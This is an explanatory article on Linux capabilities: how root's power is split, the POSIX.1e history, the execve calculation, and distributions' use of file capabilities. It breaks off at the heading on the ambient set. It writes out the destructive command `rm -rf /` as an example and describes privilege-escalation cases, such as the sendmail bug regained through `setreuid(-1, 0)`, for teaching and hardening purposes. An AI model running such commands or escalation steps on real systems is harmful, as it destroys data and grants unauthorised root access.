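# Linux capabilities: dividing the power of root into separate privileges

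## Root, setuid programs and the idea of partial privilege

Linux capabilities are named privileges that together make up the power of root, the administrator's account on Unix-like systems. A process (a running program) that holds one can do one kind of thing that the kernel, the core of the operating system, blocks ordinary users from doing, such as setting the clock or stopping another user's programs. Linux has divided root's power this way since kernel version 2.2, released in 1999, and now has 41 capabilities. How finely to divide permissions is again a practical question for people who build AI agents, which are language models that choose actions and carry them out through software tools.

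### Root and everyone else

Traditional Unix has only two classes of process, privileged and unprivileged. Each user has a numeric user ID, and every process runs under one of these IDs. When a process tries to open a file, the kernel decides whether to allow it by comparing the process's user and group IDs with the file's owner and permission settings. According to the Linux manual page *capabilities(7)*, a process with user ID 0, which belongs to root (also called the superuser), traditionally bypasses all of the kernel's permission checks. Processes with any other ID undergo the checks in full.

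*Linux Capabilities* (Hallyn and Morgan, 2008) lists why somebody must have this power: administrators have to back up data they do not own, replace failing hardware, repair other people's accidents and clear out the accounts of users who have left. But root cannot temporarily set the power aside. An ordinary user who runs `rm -rf /`, the command to delete everything on the machine, gets a harmless error message, while root has no such protection.

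Ordinary users sometimes need root's power, for example to change their passwords. Linux keeps all users' password records in one file, `/etc/shadow`. A user must be able to change her own entry but not read or change anyone else's. File permissions cannot enforce this because they apply to the whole file. Unix works around the problem with `passwd`, a program that root owns and that has its setuid bit set. When a user starts a setuid program, the kernel runs it under the ID of the file's owner instead of the user's. `passwd` therefore runs as root no matter who starts it, and can change the user's entry in `/etc/shadow`. The user does not become root but can run a program that does, and if its programmer made no mistakes, the program uses root's power only to change her password.

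While `passwd` runs, the kernel's ordinary permission checks do not restrain it, so only its own code limits what it does. Suppose that code contains a buffer overflow, a bug through which over-long input overwrites part of the program's memory and lets an attacker choose the instructions that run next. Those instructions run as root and can do things unrelated to passwords, such as starting a command shell from which the attacker can read every file, replace any program and load code into the kernel.

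Hallyn and Morgan make the same point with `ping`, which tests whether another machine answers. It needs privilege only because it builds its own network packets. Installed as a setuid-root program, it also has every other root privilege, and an attacker who found an overflow in it might gain a root shell.

Faults of this kind still turn up in programs that run as root, including some that are not setuid. SC Media's *New CIFSwitch vulnerability allows Linux privilege escalation* describes a recent case, a bug about 19 years old involving a helper program for CIFS, a protocol for sharing files over a network. The helper runs as root in response to requests that pass through the kernel. The kernel did not verify that these requests came from its own file-sharing code, so an ordinary user could forge one. The helper trusted the contents of the forged request, which allowed the attacker to run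 code as root.

### Least privilege, and privileges with names

The usual remedy is the principle of least privilege. IEEE's *Draft Standard for Information Technology* (1997), from which Linux took the idea of its capabilities, defines this as giving a program only the privileges its legitimate function requires, and only for as long as it actually requires them. For example, a server that must open one protected file when it starts has no reason to keep that privilege after opening the file.

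The group argued that most privileged programs need very little privilege. A printing service must be able to read any user's files but does not need to write to them. A login program must be able to change its user identity but does not need control over disk quotas. The group compared this to an accounting department, where the person who records the money owed to the firm is not the person who pays the bills, so that nobody can both invent a bill and write the cheque. It worried about honest mistakes as much as about crime. People forget that they are working as root and type a command that deletes files, and the system does not stop them.

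A Linux capability is a named privilege that the kernel checks for before it allows a particular kind of operation. Each thread has its own capabilities, though for most purposes one can speak of the process. *Linux Capabilities FAQ 0.2* (Tobotras, 1999) gives the example of setting the system clock. The kernel used to check whether the process's user ID was 0. With capabilities, it checks whether the process has CAP_SYS_TIME, which is stored as one bit in a row of bits. Linux gives root every capability by default, so older software works as before. But a process with another user ID can now be given CAP_SYS_TIME alone, which lets it set the clock without root's other privileges.

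Dividing root's power is meant to limit damage. An attacker who takes over a program that holds a few capabilities should be able to do less harm than if the program were running as root.

The manual entry current in January 2026 lists 41 capabilities, and there is no sign that another has been added since. In May 2026, a proposed patch to Landlock, a kernel feature for confining programs, still reserved 41 bits for capabilities (*landlock: Enforce capability restrictions*, 2026). *Capabilities update for v7.3* (2026) only corrects two comments in the capability code. Version 7.3 was out by 19 October 2026 (sk, *Linux Kernel 7.3 Is Officially Released*, 2026). A new capability could have come in through another developer's branch, so the number is very probably still 41.

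The 41 capabilities vary greatly in how much they allow. CAP_SYS_TIME only lets a process set the system and hardware clocks. CAP_KILL lets a process send signals (short messages, some of which end the program that receives them) to any process, not just those of the same user. Port numbers distinguish the network services on one machine, and Linux reserves the numbers below 1024. With CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE, a web server can use its usual port, 80, without being root.

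CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE lets a process bypass the permission checks on reading, writing and executing files. DAC stands for "discretionary access control", the system of permissions that owners set on their files. A program with this capability is much more dangerous if an attacker takes it over than one with CAP_SYS_TIME, because the attacker could access everyone's files rather than just change the clock. The Linux man-pages describe CAP_NET_BROADCAST as unused, while CAP_SYS_ADMIN covers many operations that have little in common.

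### The POSIX.1e draft

Both the scheme and its confusing name come from an attempt to add security extensions to POSIX, a family of IEEE standards for the programming interface of Unix-like systems. A POSIX group was working on the extensions by 1989, and it then used the term "privileges". *Standards Update, IEEE 1003.6*, a report on the group from that year, gives "priv_" as the agreed prefix for the functions concerned. De Alvare (1991), in *Report on POSIX.6*, still wrote of a "Privilege subgroup" at a Chicago meeting that prepared draft 11. The group later switched to "capability", on the ground that "privilege" meant something else entirely in international usage. The new name also caused confusion, since "capability" already had a settled meaning in computer science.

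Draft 17, of October 1997, covered five optional subjects: access control lists (file permissions that can name individual users and groups), auditing, capabilities, mandatory access control (rules that the system enforces regardless of the file owner's wishes) and information labels. A system that adopted the capability part had to provide at least eleven capabilities, and more if it adopted some of the other parts.

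The group wrote down how it had arrived at them. It went through the existing POSIX documents in search of the phrase "appropriate privilege", which marks the places where an action fails unless the process has special rights, and also looked for requirements that the text merely implied. It then put identical or nearly identical requirements together and gave each bundle a name. Three guidelines governed the bundling:

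- A capability should exempt a process from one specific security requirement.
- Capabilities should overlap as little as possible, so that an administrator who grants several of them can be confident that they do not add up to another one that she withheld.
- Within those limits, fewer are better. A separate capability for every requirement would have meant several hundred of them, and the group foresaw "a management nightmare".

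The IEEE group admitted that these guidelines partly contradict each other, as its treatment of file permissions shows. It considered a single capability, CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE, for bypassing all file permissions, and rejected it as too coarse because a backup program must read every file on the system but needs to write only to the backup device. It also considered four capabilities, for reading, writing, searching directories and executing. Programs that had to read everything would also have to search everything, so four seemed more than anyone needed, and the draft ended up with three.

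The group called the new interfaces necessary but not sufficient for least privilege. Somebody still has to work out which capabilities each program should have.

The draft never became a standard. Truemper (1999), in *Security extensions to Posix (what would have been Posix.1e/2c)*, wrote that IEEE had dropped it the year before because nobody could tell when it would be finished. According to Tobotras, the committee had by then worked on it for more than ten years. Casey Schaufler of the computer maker SGI, the draft's last technical editor, gave the fullest account in reply to a Usenet question from Peter (2002), *Posix.1e?*. Schaufler said that he had requested the withdrawal himself. He said that only SGI and IBM were still interested enough to continue, that IBM would not pay for travel, and that computer companies had generally lost interest in standards around 1995.

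He also complained that the document's five subjects should have been separate efforts, that the committee had designed too much of the content itself, and that the source text had disappeared for a year and only part of it had come back. He answered "Yes" when asked whether the reasons were technical or political, implying that they were both.

Hallyn and Morgan instead emphasize the decline of the commercial Unix vendors in the later 1990s, which they connect with the rise of Linux. The two explanations are compatible, since those vendors would have had to pay for the work. Schaufler did not single out the division of root's power as a bad idea in his complaints, and he considered the effort a success in one respect, because many systems had implemented parts of the draft anyway.

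### From Linux-Privs to the kernel

The Linux specification in Morgan (1997), in *Linux-Privs*, is dated 21 April 1997, six months before Draft 17. Its main aim was to separate identity from privilege. Under the old model the two were joined, because user 0 was all-powerful. Under the new one, capabilities would belong to particular applications, and a user could exercise them only through those applications and only for what the applications were built to do. Hallyn and Morgan later summarized this as "programs, not people, exercise privilege".

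Morgan described the specification as compatible with POSIX.1e as far as possible "without open access to the actual specifications". Some of the text seems to reflect this lack of access. For example, the entry for CAP_FSETID, which concerns special permission bits on files, has the description that belongs to CAP_KILL. The list also included the single CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE that IEEE's group had judged too coarse. Linux still has it, though a backup program needs only the weaker CAP_DAC_READ_SEARCH, which covers only reading files and reading and searching directories.

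Morgan's list had 51 capabilities, many of them narrow. Inserting and removing kernel modules each had its own capability, as did configuring the firewall, the network interfaces and the routing tables. The code went into the kernel during the 2.1 development series and reached general use with the stable version 2.2, but capabilities could not be attached to program files until 2.6.24. To judge by the version numbers in the manual, Linux 2.2 started with 27 capabilities, roughly half as many as Morgan's list. Some of the difference comes from dropping the parts that depended on other POSIX.1e subjects, and some from merging. CAP_SYS_MODULE now covers both loading and unloading modules, and CAP_NET_ADMIN covers the firewall, the interfaces and the routing tables. Kernel developers have added 14 capabilities since, most recently CAP_CHECKPOINT_RESTORE in version 5.9.

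In the kernel's header file for capabilities, Morgan and Kjeldaas, in *Linux kernel mirror (for testing)*, still refer programmers to a library that complies with Section 25 of Draft 17, even though that draft was withdrawn.

### The other meaning of "capability"

In computer science, "capability" had long meant an unforgeable reference to one object, together with rights over that object. This is now usually called an "object capability". The similar names often cause confusion, and Tobotras began his FAQ by distinguishing the two. An object capability refers to a particular object, whereas a Linux capability refers to a class of operations on any object.

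A file descriptor names an object and is a capability in the older sense. When a process asks to open a file for reading, the kernel checks the permissions once, records the file and the permitted operations in a table, and gives the process a file descriptor, a number that marks the entry's position in the table. On every later read, the kernel only has to look up the entry. The process cannot make up an entry, because the table is in the kernel's memory. It can pass the descriptor to another process, which can then read that file without gaining access to any other.

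A process that holds CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE can read and write any file, including files created later, even when the file's ordinary permissions would forbid it. The holder cannot limit the capability to particular files because, as Tobotras points out, Linux has no way to make a "subcapability" out of a capability. Similarly, a web server that needs port 80 gets CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE, which also lets it use every other port below 1024.

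The difference shows when someone tricks a program that otherwise works correctly. For example, a user might give the name of the password file to a program that copies files for users and has CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE. Unless the programmer anticipated this, the program will open the file, because the kernel skips the permission check for any name it receives. If the user had to pass an open file descriptor instead, the program could copy only what the user had been able to open. Dividing root's power limits the kinds of operation an attacker can perform, but does much less to limit which files or other objects the attacker can perform them on.

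Capsicum, part of FreeBSD since version 9.0, extends file descriptors into a general system of object capabilities. Once a process enters capability mode, it can no longer look up files by name in the file system as a whole, and must work with descriptors it already has or that other processes pass to it.

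## The capability sets of processes and files

When a process tries to set the clock, the kernel checks whether CAP_SYS_TIME is currently in force for that process. The process may also have capabilities that it has switched off, and some that it can pass to the next program it runs. Linux tracks these in separate sets, each with room for 64 capabilities.

### The four sets of a process

The effective set contains the capabilities now in force. The kernel checks only this set when deciding whether to allow an operation. The permitted set contains the capabilities that the process may put into force. A process can use the system call `capset` to switch any permitted capability on or off in its effective set, any number of times. It can also use `capset` to remove capabilities from its permitted set, but not to add them.

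A program that corrects the clock once an hour could keep CAP_SYS_TIME in its permitted set and switch it on only during each correction. If a bug made the program try to change the clock at another time, the attempt would fail. This protects much less against an attacker who can run code inside the process, because that code can also call `capset` to switch the capability on. Only removing the capability from the permitted set prevents this. The process can then regain it only by running a setuid-root program or a program file that grants it.

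The inheritable set contains the capabilities that a process can pass to a new program when it calls `execve`. When a user types a command, the shell copies itself with the system call `fork`, and the copy calls `execve` to replace its program with the requested one. `fork` copies all the capability sets unchanged, but the kernel recalculates them at `execve`. The new program receives the inheritable capabilities only if its file also allows them.

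A process can remove any capability from its inheritable set. It can add one only if that capability is already in its permitted set or if CAP_SETPCAP is in its effective set. According to Hallyn and Morgan, `init`, the ancestor of all other processes, starts with an empty inheritable set, so processes inherit no capabilities this way unless a program adds them to the set. CAP_SETPCAP once had a different purpose, which was to let one process change another's capabilities without notifying it. This was so dangerous that kernel developers kept it disabled from the start.

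The bounding set limits the capabilities that a program file can grant. It is full when `init` starts, and every child process gets a copy of its parent's. A process with CAP_SETPCAP can remove capabilities from its own bounding set, but no process can put one back. A process also cannot add a capability to its inheritable set unless that capability is in its bounding set.

Until Linux 2.6.25, the whole machine shared one bounding set. An administrator could use it to stop anyone from loading kernel modules, but could not restrict only one group of programs. Hallyn and Morgan explain that Linux switched to a separate bounding set for each process because of containers, which are groups of processes isolated from the rest of the system. Someone who sets up a container can now remove CAP_MKNOD from its bounding set, for example, so that programs inside cannot create device files and use them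 to access the hardware.

However, removing a capability from the bounding set does not remove it from the inheritable set. A process that still has CAP_MKNOD in its inheritable set can obtain it by running a program whose file allows the inheritance. Whoever builds the container must therefore remove the capability from both sets. Hallyn and Morgan suggest that one might occasionally leave it in the inheritable set on purpose, so that only one trusted program in the container can create its device files.

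Linux 4.3 added a fifth set, the ambient set, for passing capabilities to ordinary programs. It appears in the formula below, but readers can treat it as empty for now.

### Capabilities attached to files

An administrator attaches capabilities to a program with the `setcap` command. The command stores them in `security.capability`, an extended attribute, which is a named piece of data that the file system keeps alongside a file. Writing to this attribute requires CAP_SETFCAP. Otherwise, any user could write a program, give it every capability and run it.

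The attribute has three parts:

- The file permitted set lists capabilities that the program receives whoever runs it, as far as the bounding set allows. An older name for it is the "forced" set.
- The file inheritable set lists capabilities that the program receives only if the process running it has them in its own inheritable set.
- The file effective part is a single bit. If it is 1, the program starts with all its new permitted capabilities switched on. If it is 0, the program starts with them switched off and has to switch them on itself.

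`setcap` uses the letters e, i and p for the effective, inheritable and permitted parts, so `cap_net_raw=ep` puts CAP_NET_RAW in the file permitted set and also marks it as effective. As Hallyn explains in *Making Root Unprivileged*, `setcap` returns an error if an administrator tries to mark only some of a file's capabilities as effective, even though the notation suggests that she could.

Hallyn calls the bit the "legacy bit" and argues that one is enough because there are two kinds of program. A program written with capabilities in mind should start with none in force and turn on those it needs. An older program has no code to turn them on, so every capability it may use has to be in force from the start. He saw no use for starting a program with only some of its capabilities in force.

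The original format of the attribute had room for 32 capabilities, and Linux 2.6.25 extended it to 64. Linux 4.14 added a version that grants capabilities only inside a particular user namespace. The kernel ignores the attribute whenever it ignores the setuid bit, and an administrator can also turn file capabilities off at boot.

### The calculation at execve

According to the Linux man-pages, the kernel calculates the new permitted and effective sets like this:

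```
new permitted = (inheritable & file inheritable)
              | (file permitted & bounding)
              | new ambient

new effective = new permitted, if the file's effective bit is 1
                new ambient, if the bit is 0
```

Names that begin with "file" refer to parts of the file's attribute, names that begin with "new" refer to the process's sets after `execve`, and the other names refer to the process's sets before it. `&` gives the capabilities that are in both sets, and `|` gives those that are in either. `execve` does not change the inheritable and bounding sets.

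A capability can enter the new permitted set through any of the three lines. The line `inheritable & file inheritable` adds a capability only if it is in the inheritable sets of both the process and the file. Hallyn and Morgan demonstrate this with `rm`, the file-deletion command. If an administrator put CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE in `rm`'s file permitted set, every user could delete everyone else's files. Instead, they put it in the file inheritable set and configured the login system to add it to the inheritable set of one user, a student administrator. She could then delete root's files with `rm`, while `rm` worked as before for other users. When she tried to delete another of root's files with `unlink`, she got an error because `unlink` had no capabilities attached.

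The term `file permitted & bounding` does not depend on the process's inheritable set. The process gains every capability in the file's permitted set that is also in the bounding set. This replaces the setuid bit as a way to give a program privileges its caller lacks.

`new ambient` is the set of capabilities that a process passes to a program with no file capabilities. The kernel empties this set if the program is setuid or has file capabilities.

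The formula does not include the old permitted set, so a process running as an ordinary user with empty inheritable and ambient sets loses all its capabilities when it runs a program with no file capabilities.

### Three ways to run ping

`ping` needs only the CAP_NET_RAW capability and has long been the standard example for file capabilities. Suppose an ordinary user runs it from a shell with empty inheritable and ambient sets and a full bounding set.

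In the simplest arrangement, the administrator has removed the setuid bit and marked the file `cap_net_raw=ep`. The file inheritable set is empty, so the first line of the formula gives nothing. The file permitted set contains CAP_NET_RAW, which is also in the bounding set, so it passes:

```
new permitted = {} | {CAP_NET_RAW} | {} = {CAP_NET_RAW}
new effective = new permitted           = {CAP_NET_RAW}
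```

`ping` works without any change to its code. An attacker who takes it over can send forged packets but gets none of root's other powers. Hallyn and Morgan caution that the attacker might still use a forged packet to attack another privileged program.

Now suppose that the administrator marks the file `cap_net_raw=p`. The new permitted set is the same, but the effective bit is 0, so the new effective set is empty. An old version of `ping` would therefore fail when it tried to open its network socket. Hallyn and Morgan show how a programmer can change the program to switch CAP_NET_RAW on, perform the privileged operation and switch the capability off again. When the program no longer needs the capability, it also removes it from the permitted set. If a bug then occurs elsewhere in `ping`, such as in the code that reads replies from the network, the process has no privilege left. Recent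 versions of `ping` seem to work this way. The error message in Ubuntu's *iputils 3:20240905-1 doesn't work for unprivileged users* lists the required capability as "cap_net_raw+p", without the e.

In the last arrangement the file again has `cap_net_raw=ep`, but someone has removed CAP_NET_RAW from the shell's bounding set:

```
new permitted = {} | ({CAP_NET_RAW} & bounding) | {} = {}
```

The kernel compares this result with the file permitted set and finds that the program would start without at least one capability in that set. `execve` then fails with the error EPERM, "operation not permitted", so `ping` never runs.

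This precaution hardly matters for `ping`. When Hallyn and Morgan tried the same thing in 2008, before the kernel had this check, `ping` started, failed to open its socket and stopped with an error message. But the effective bit marks a program that was not written to use capabilities, so the program cannot check its own sets for missing ones. If it performs several privileged steps, the earlier ones may succeed and a later one may fail where its programmer never expected failure. Hallyn and Morgan therefore proposed that the kernel should refuse to start such a program when capabilities are missing, and the kernel now does.

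The check does not apply to a file marked only `p`, because a program that switches on its own capabilities can also test whether it has them. If `ping` gets CAP_NET_RAW through the inheritable sets, it starts despite the reduced bounding set, because it has every capability in its file's permitted set.

### Why root still has everything

Most programs on a Linux system have no capabilities attached. If the kernel applied the formula to them as it stands, root would lose all its power on running its first command. So the kernel makes an exception for user ID 0. When root runs a program, or anyone runs a setuid-root program, the kernel normally treats the file as if its permitted and inheritable sets contained every capability and its effective bit were 1. The formula then reduces to

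```
new permitted = inheritable | bounding
new effective = new permitted
```

With a full bounding set, the result is every capability. Hallyn and Morgan describe this as using capabilities to implement the superuser, so that the kernel needs only one privilege mechanism.

That exception does not apply when an ordinary user runs a setuid-root program that also has file capabilities. The kernel instead uses the capabilities on the file. A setuid-root program with an empty set attached therefore runs as user 0 but gains no capabilities by doing so.

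The kernel also reproduces the traditional effect of a program giving up root. A process has a real user ID, which identifies who started it, an effective user ID, which the kernel uses for most permission checks, and a saved user ID, which lets the process return to an earlier identity. When a process changes its effective ID from 0 to something else, the kernel clears its effective capability set. When none of the three IDs is 0 any longer, the kernel clears the permitted set too. When a process changes its effective ID back to 0, the kernel copies the permitted set into the effective set.

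The securebits flags turn off these special rules for root. SECBIT_NOROOT stops the kernel from granting capabilities because of user ID 0 at `execve`, and SECBIT_NO_SETUID_FIXUP stops it from adjusting the sets when user IDs change. The narrower SECBIT_KEEP_CAPS lets a server start as root, change to an ordinary user ID and keep its permitted capabilities, though it then has to switch on the ones it needs. Each flag has a companion flag that locks it permanently. Changing the flags requires CAP_SETPCAP. Child processes inherit the flags, so one part of a system can run without a privileged root while the rest is unaffected.

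Hallyn tried this on Fedora 10, a Linux distribution (a kernel packaged with other programs). He first used a small program to set and lock the flags and then start `sshd`, the server for remote logins. `sshd` failed because, after changing to an unprivileged identity, it tests that it cannot change back. Now it could, because the kernel no longer removed the capabilities for changing IDs. Hallyn removed the test, but acknowledged that the right solution was to separate the handling of privilege from the handling of user IDs in `sshd`'s code. When he then logged in as root, he had no capabilities.

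Hallyn next created administrative users with a few capabilities each. The one responsible for user accounts could not change anyone's password, because `passwd` does its own check for user ID 0 and printed "Only root can specify a user name". Hallyn got around this by giving that administrator the user ID 0, which by then carried no privilege. To get the machine to start up, he also had to attach capabilities to several dozen system programs, and he allowed most of them all capabilities. He called the result a "lazy prototype", but it shows that the kernel can run without a privileged root, and that much of the remaining work lies in programs that decide whether an action is allowed by checking whether the user ID is 0.

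A root user without capabilities still has more power than an ordinary user. Hallyn and Morgan point out that root owns many important files, including much of `/etc`, which holds system settings. A process with user ID 0 can change those files as their owner.

### The sendmail bug

In June 2000, an ordinary user could become root on Linux by taking a privilege away from a program. The best-known target was sendmail, a widely used mail server. When a user submitted a message, sendmail ran as a setuid-root program because ordinary users could not write to the mail queue. Before doing anything risky on the user's behalf, it gave up root permanently by calling `setuid(getuid())`, which set its user ID to that of the person who had started it.

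The `setuid` call changes the real, effective and saved user IDs if the process has what POSIX terms "appropriate privileges". Otherwise it changes only the effective user ID. On Linux the appropriate privilege is CAP_SETUID, which a setuid-root program normally had.

Linux could not yet attach capabilities to files, so the kernel made up file sets for root's programs, though differently from today. It gave every process a full inheritable set. For a setuid-root program, it treated the file inheritable set as full and the file permitted set as empty, so the formula made the program's new permitted set equal to the inheritable set of the process that started it. Any process may remove capabilities from its inheritable set, so a user could remove CAP_SETUID from hers and then start sendmail, which would run as user 0 with every capability except that one.

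When sendmail tried to give up root, `setuid` changed the effective user ID, left the saved ID at 0 and reported success. Chen, Wagner and Dean (2002), in *Setuid Demystified*, attribute many security holes to confusion over such calls. In this case, they describe an attacker who takes over sendmail at this stage, perhaps through a buffer overflow, and calls `setreuid(-1, 0)` to restore root from the saved ID. Hallyn and Morgan's shorter account requires no overflow, because sendmail itself started a program as root when it should have been running as the user.

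Wojciech Purczynski (2000) discovered the problem while programming a kernel module, as he reported in *Sendmail & procmail local root exploits on Linux kernel up to 2.2.16pre5*. He produced two working exploits and found that procmail, a program for sorting mail, was also vulnerable. In its advisory, Sendmail (2000) attributed the problem to kernel versions up to 2.2.15 and recommended upgrading to 2.2.16 as the only way to protect every program on the machine.

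It also warned programmers that checking the result of `setuid` would not help, because the call succeeded whether or not the program lost its root privileges. A new version of sendmail instead tried to regain root after giving it up, and refused to continue if the attempt worked. The `sshd` test that got in Hallyn's way makes the same kind of check.

The kernel developers fixed the calculation by giving processes an empty inheritable set and treating the file permitted set of a setuid-root program as full. The current rule has the same effect. Root's new permitted set is `inheritable | bounding`, so removing CAP_SETUID from the inheritable set doesn't remove it from the permitted set if the bounding set still contains it, and an ordinary user cannot change the bounding set.

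Sendmail became more dangerous when it ran without CAP_SETUID, the capability that lets a process take on other users' identities. A root process also uses this capability to give up its own identity. Sendmail's programmers had written it for a system on which root had either all its powers or none. Taking one privilege away from such a program puts it in a state that nobody designed or tested.

A very similar problem appeared in Linux again in 2014. Andy Lutomirski (2014), in *local privilege escalation due to capng_lock as used in seunshare*, examined a setuid-root tool that ran other programs in a restricted environment. The tool locked the securebits so that nothing inside could regain capabilities. As Alpine Linux's report on libcap-ng explains, a setuid-root program started there ran as user 0 without capabilities. Lutomirski wrote a short test program that gave up root with `setuid(getuid())`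 and then tried to get it back. The program failed to regain root when run normally but succeeded when run through the tool.

People discussing the report disagreed about whose fault this was. Steve Grubb of Red Hat thought the test program was wrong because it should have used `setresuid`, which sets all three IDs explicitly. Solar Designer of the security project Openwall replied that correct programs written for traditional Unix must stay safe on Linux, and called the flaw "a reincarnation" of the sendmail bug. His argument seems stronger, since an administrator cannot rewrite every old program before restricting it.

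Lutomirski concluded that no setting of the flags would make setuid programs safe in that environment. Running them without capabilities was unsafe, and running them with capabilities and user ID 0 seemed unsafe too. The remaining choice was to give them no extra privileges. Linux's `no_new_privs` setting does this by preventing `execve` from granting new privileges, so a setuid-root program runs as the user who started it. According to Red Hat's *CVE-2014-3215*, the kernel part of the company's fix added this setting to its systems.

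Some of the danger remains, because the EPERM check protects only programs with file capabilities. A setuid-root program without them still starts when its bounding set lacks a capability, and Hallyn and Morgan expected many old programs to have sendmail's weakness. But reducing the bounding set now requires CAP_SETPCAP, so the hazard comes from administrators trying to make a system safer. Hallyn and Morgan advise against using the bounding set as a general way to reduce privilege, and prefer to grant optional capabilities through the inheritable set.

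### Programs, not people

Hallyn and Morgan justify these mechanisms by observing that users never do anything privileged directly. Programs do it for them, and a privilege is safe only if the program exercising it was written to handle it. When privilege belongs to user ID 0, every program that root starts has all of it, including a game or a text editor whose author never thought about security. They call this arbitrary. With file capabilities, an administrator can instead decide program by program which privileges to grant, using what she knows about what the program does, who wrote it and who installed it.

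The argument fits `ping` well because `ping` does one thing and does it the same way for everybody. It fits `rm` less well because `rm` deletes whatever its user names, so whether it should be able to delete other people's files depends on who runs it. Hallyn and Morgan therefore needed the inheritable sets for `rm`, and in their example the privilege is granted only when a particular person runs a particular program. This is still considerably safer than traditional root, because a malicious program that the student administrator runs by accident gets no capabilities. But if that program can start `rm` on her behalf, it can still delete root's files.

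`su` is at the far end of this range. It lets a user become another user, usually root, and then run anything. A maintainer commenting in Red Hat Bugzilla saw no way to use file capabilities for it, "since the admin would need all capabilities once he becomes root".

### What distributions did with file capabilities

For years, capabilities offered Linux users little benefit. In September 2006, LWN's *A bid to resurrect Linux capabilities* reported no known successful distribution based on them. One reason was that the kernel could not yet attach capabilities to files. Another was that nobody had worked out how to administer a system with a couple of dozen extra security settings on every program.

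Linux 2.6.24 removed the first obstacle to using file capabilities by adding kernel support for them. *Filesystem capabilities in Fedora 10* (Edge, 2009) reported that by January 2009 Fedora had everything it needed to use them, but neither it nor any other mainstream distribution did so by default. Fedora's developers had tried to convert `ping` to file capabilities and given up. Some users built their own kernels without this support, and a contributor to Fedora's development list pointed out that packages containing file capabilities would not install on those machines. Ulrich Drepper, one of the developers, called this concern "nonsense", because Fedora already depended on many other optional kernel features. Linux 2.6.33 removed the option to build a kernel without file capabilities.

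Fedora's *Lower Process Capabilities* (2009), a project for version 12, at first kept background services running as root but reduced their capabilities. A year later, Fedora had a more ambitious plan. Solar Designer noted in *filesystem capabilities* (2010) that both Fedora and Ubuntu were moving towards replacing the setuid bit, and a draft release note in Fedora's *Replace setuid apps where possible with file capabilities* announced that Fedora 15 "removes setuid applications".

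The maintainers of individual packages had to do the work, and several asked how to find out which capabilities their programs needed. A critic on Fedora's wiki (2010) observed that `ls -l`, the usual command for inspecting files, shows the setuid bit but not capabilities, so administrators would find it harder to see which programs were privileged. The critic also wanted tests of the tools that copy and back up files. The archiving programs `tar` and `cpio` did drop the capabilities when Fedora 15 and later systems were packed for use in containers. In *etc/dists/scripts/postcreate.sh*, Kir Kolyshkin used a script to restore them after unpacking.

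Some conversions succeeded, including that of a package of security tools that contained one of the setuid programs on the list. The value of a conversion depended on which capabilities the program needed. The example Fedora gave maintainers to follow was the X server, which draws the graphical display. According to Red Hat Bugzilla, its new capabilities were CAP_SYS_ADMIN, CAP_SYS_RAWIO and CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE. CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE alone lets an attacker overwrite any file, so taking over the new X server would have been nearly as useful to an attacker as taking over the old one. An LWN reader, nelhage (2010), in *Fedora to (try to) remove setuid files for F15*, expected little benefit for a similar reason, since `su` and `sudo` would still need capabilities that an attacker could easily turn into full privilege.

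The plan was only partly carried out. Daniel Walsh (2010), the project's owner, filed requests for individual packages, and one stayed open until February 2015, long after Fedora 15. `su` and `sudo` still run as setuid-root programs on the major distributions. There seems to be no current count of how many programs use each method across distributions.

At the start of 2023, Noah Meyerhans of Debian wrote that the distribution's `ping` got CAP_NET_RAW either from its file or through the setuid bit. Debian's *NEWS* (2025) announces that `ping` now has neither, and Debian's package listing places the change in Debian 13. The program uses a kind of network socket, available in the kernel since 2011, that can send `ping`'s messages but not arbitrary packets. A system setting determines which groups of users may open such a socket, and normal Debian installations allow nearly everyone.

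Ubuntu picked up the new package before it had adopted the setting, so `ping` stopped working for ordinary users there. With the setting in place, this version of `ping` is safer than one with a file capability. An attacker who takes it over gains no privilege, because the kernel developers made the one harmless operation it needs available without privilege.

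## Passing capabilities to other programs

A file capability works well for `ping`, which does its own privileged work. Many services start other programs to do parts of the job, and those programs need the privilege. Every program that root runs is privileged, but until 2015, an ordinary user's process that held a few capabilities had no practical way to pass them on to the programs it started.

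### Why the inheritable set passes on so little

Despite its name, the inheritable set gives a new program a capability only if the program's file allows the same capability, and almost no files on a Linux system do. If a service adds CAP_NET_ADMIN, the capability for configuring the network, to its inheritable set and starts an ordinary helper program, the helper starts without the capability in its permitted set. CAP_NET_ADMIN stays in the helper's inheritable set, but it has no effect unless the helper or a later program in the chain runs a file that allows it.

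Lutomirski (2015), in *[RFC] capabilities*, called capability inheritance "basically useless" for this reason. He considered giving nearly every program on the machine a full file inheritable set, which would make inheritance work as people expect. However, most file systems at the time could not store the attribute. Also, when an ordinary user runs a program that gets capabilities through its file, the program starts in a "secure execution" mode, in which it ignores environment variables such as `LD_PRELOAD`. A user can normally set `LD_PRELOAD` to load her own library into a program, which would let her take over the privilege of a privileged program. The mode is a sensible precaution for `ping`, but Lutomirski found that applying it to every program breaks many of them.

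Christoph Lameter needed both inheritance and `LD_PRELOAD`. He worked with software that controls network cards directly, bypassing the kernel's network code, as some scientific computing and high-frequency trading systems do. The software needed three capabilities, for raw network access, network configuration and real-time scheduling. Scripts that could run arbitrary other programs started it, and some of it relied on `LD_PRELOAD`. Lameter (2015), in *[capabilities] Allow normal inheritance for a configurable set of capabilities* reported that he had been using a privately modified kernel in production for six years to make this work without running everything as root.

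### The Chrome OS network daemon

Google's Chrome OS had the same difficulty with a daemon, a program that runs in the background. Kees Cook, who worked on Chrome OS security, describes the case in *security things in Linux v4.3* (2016). The daemon managed network services and called helper tools to carry out networking operations. The developers did not want to run the daemon as root, but the helpers needed some of its capabilities.

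Suppose that the daemon has CAP_NET_ADMIN in its permitted, effective and inheritable sets, and runs a helper with no file capabilities. Without an ambient set, the calculation at `execve` is:

```
new permitted = ({CAP_NET_ADMIN} & {}) | ({} & bounding) = {}
new effective = {}
```

The helper could not configure anything, so the developers had to put CAP_NET_ADMIN in the file inheritable set of each helper. If the daemon ran a shell script that called the helper, the shell's file needed the same setting for any privileged steps in the script itself to work. Cook's example of how bad this could get is that one might have to set file capabilities on `bash`, the standard command shell. The settings on different files could also conflict, because the same tool may need a capability in one part of the system and not in another.

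In March 2015 Cook wrote that Chrome OS was still managing with file capabilities because its process tree was very small. A larger system would have needed a correct list of capabilities for every program its services might run.

### The ambient set

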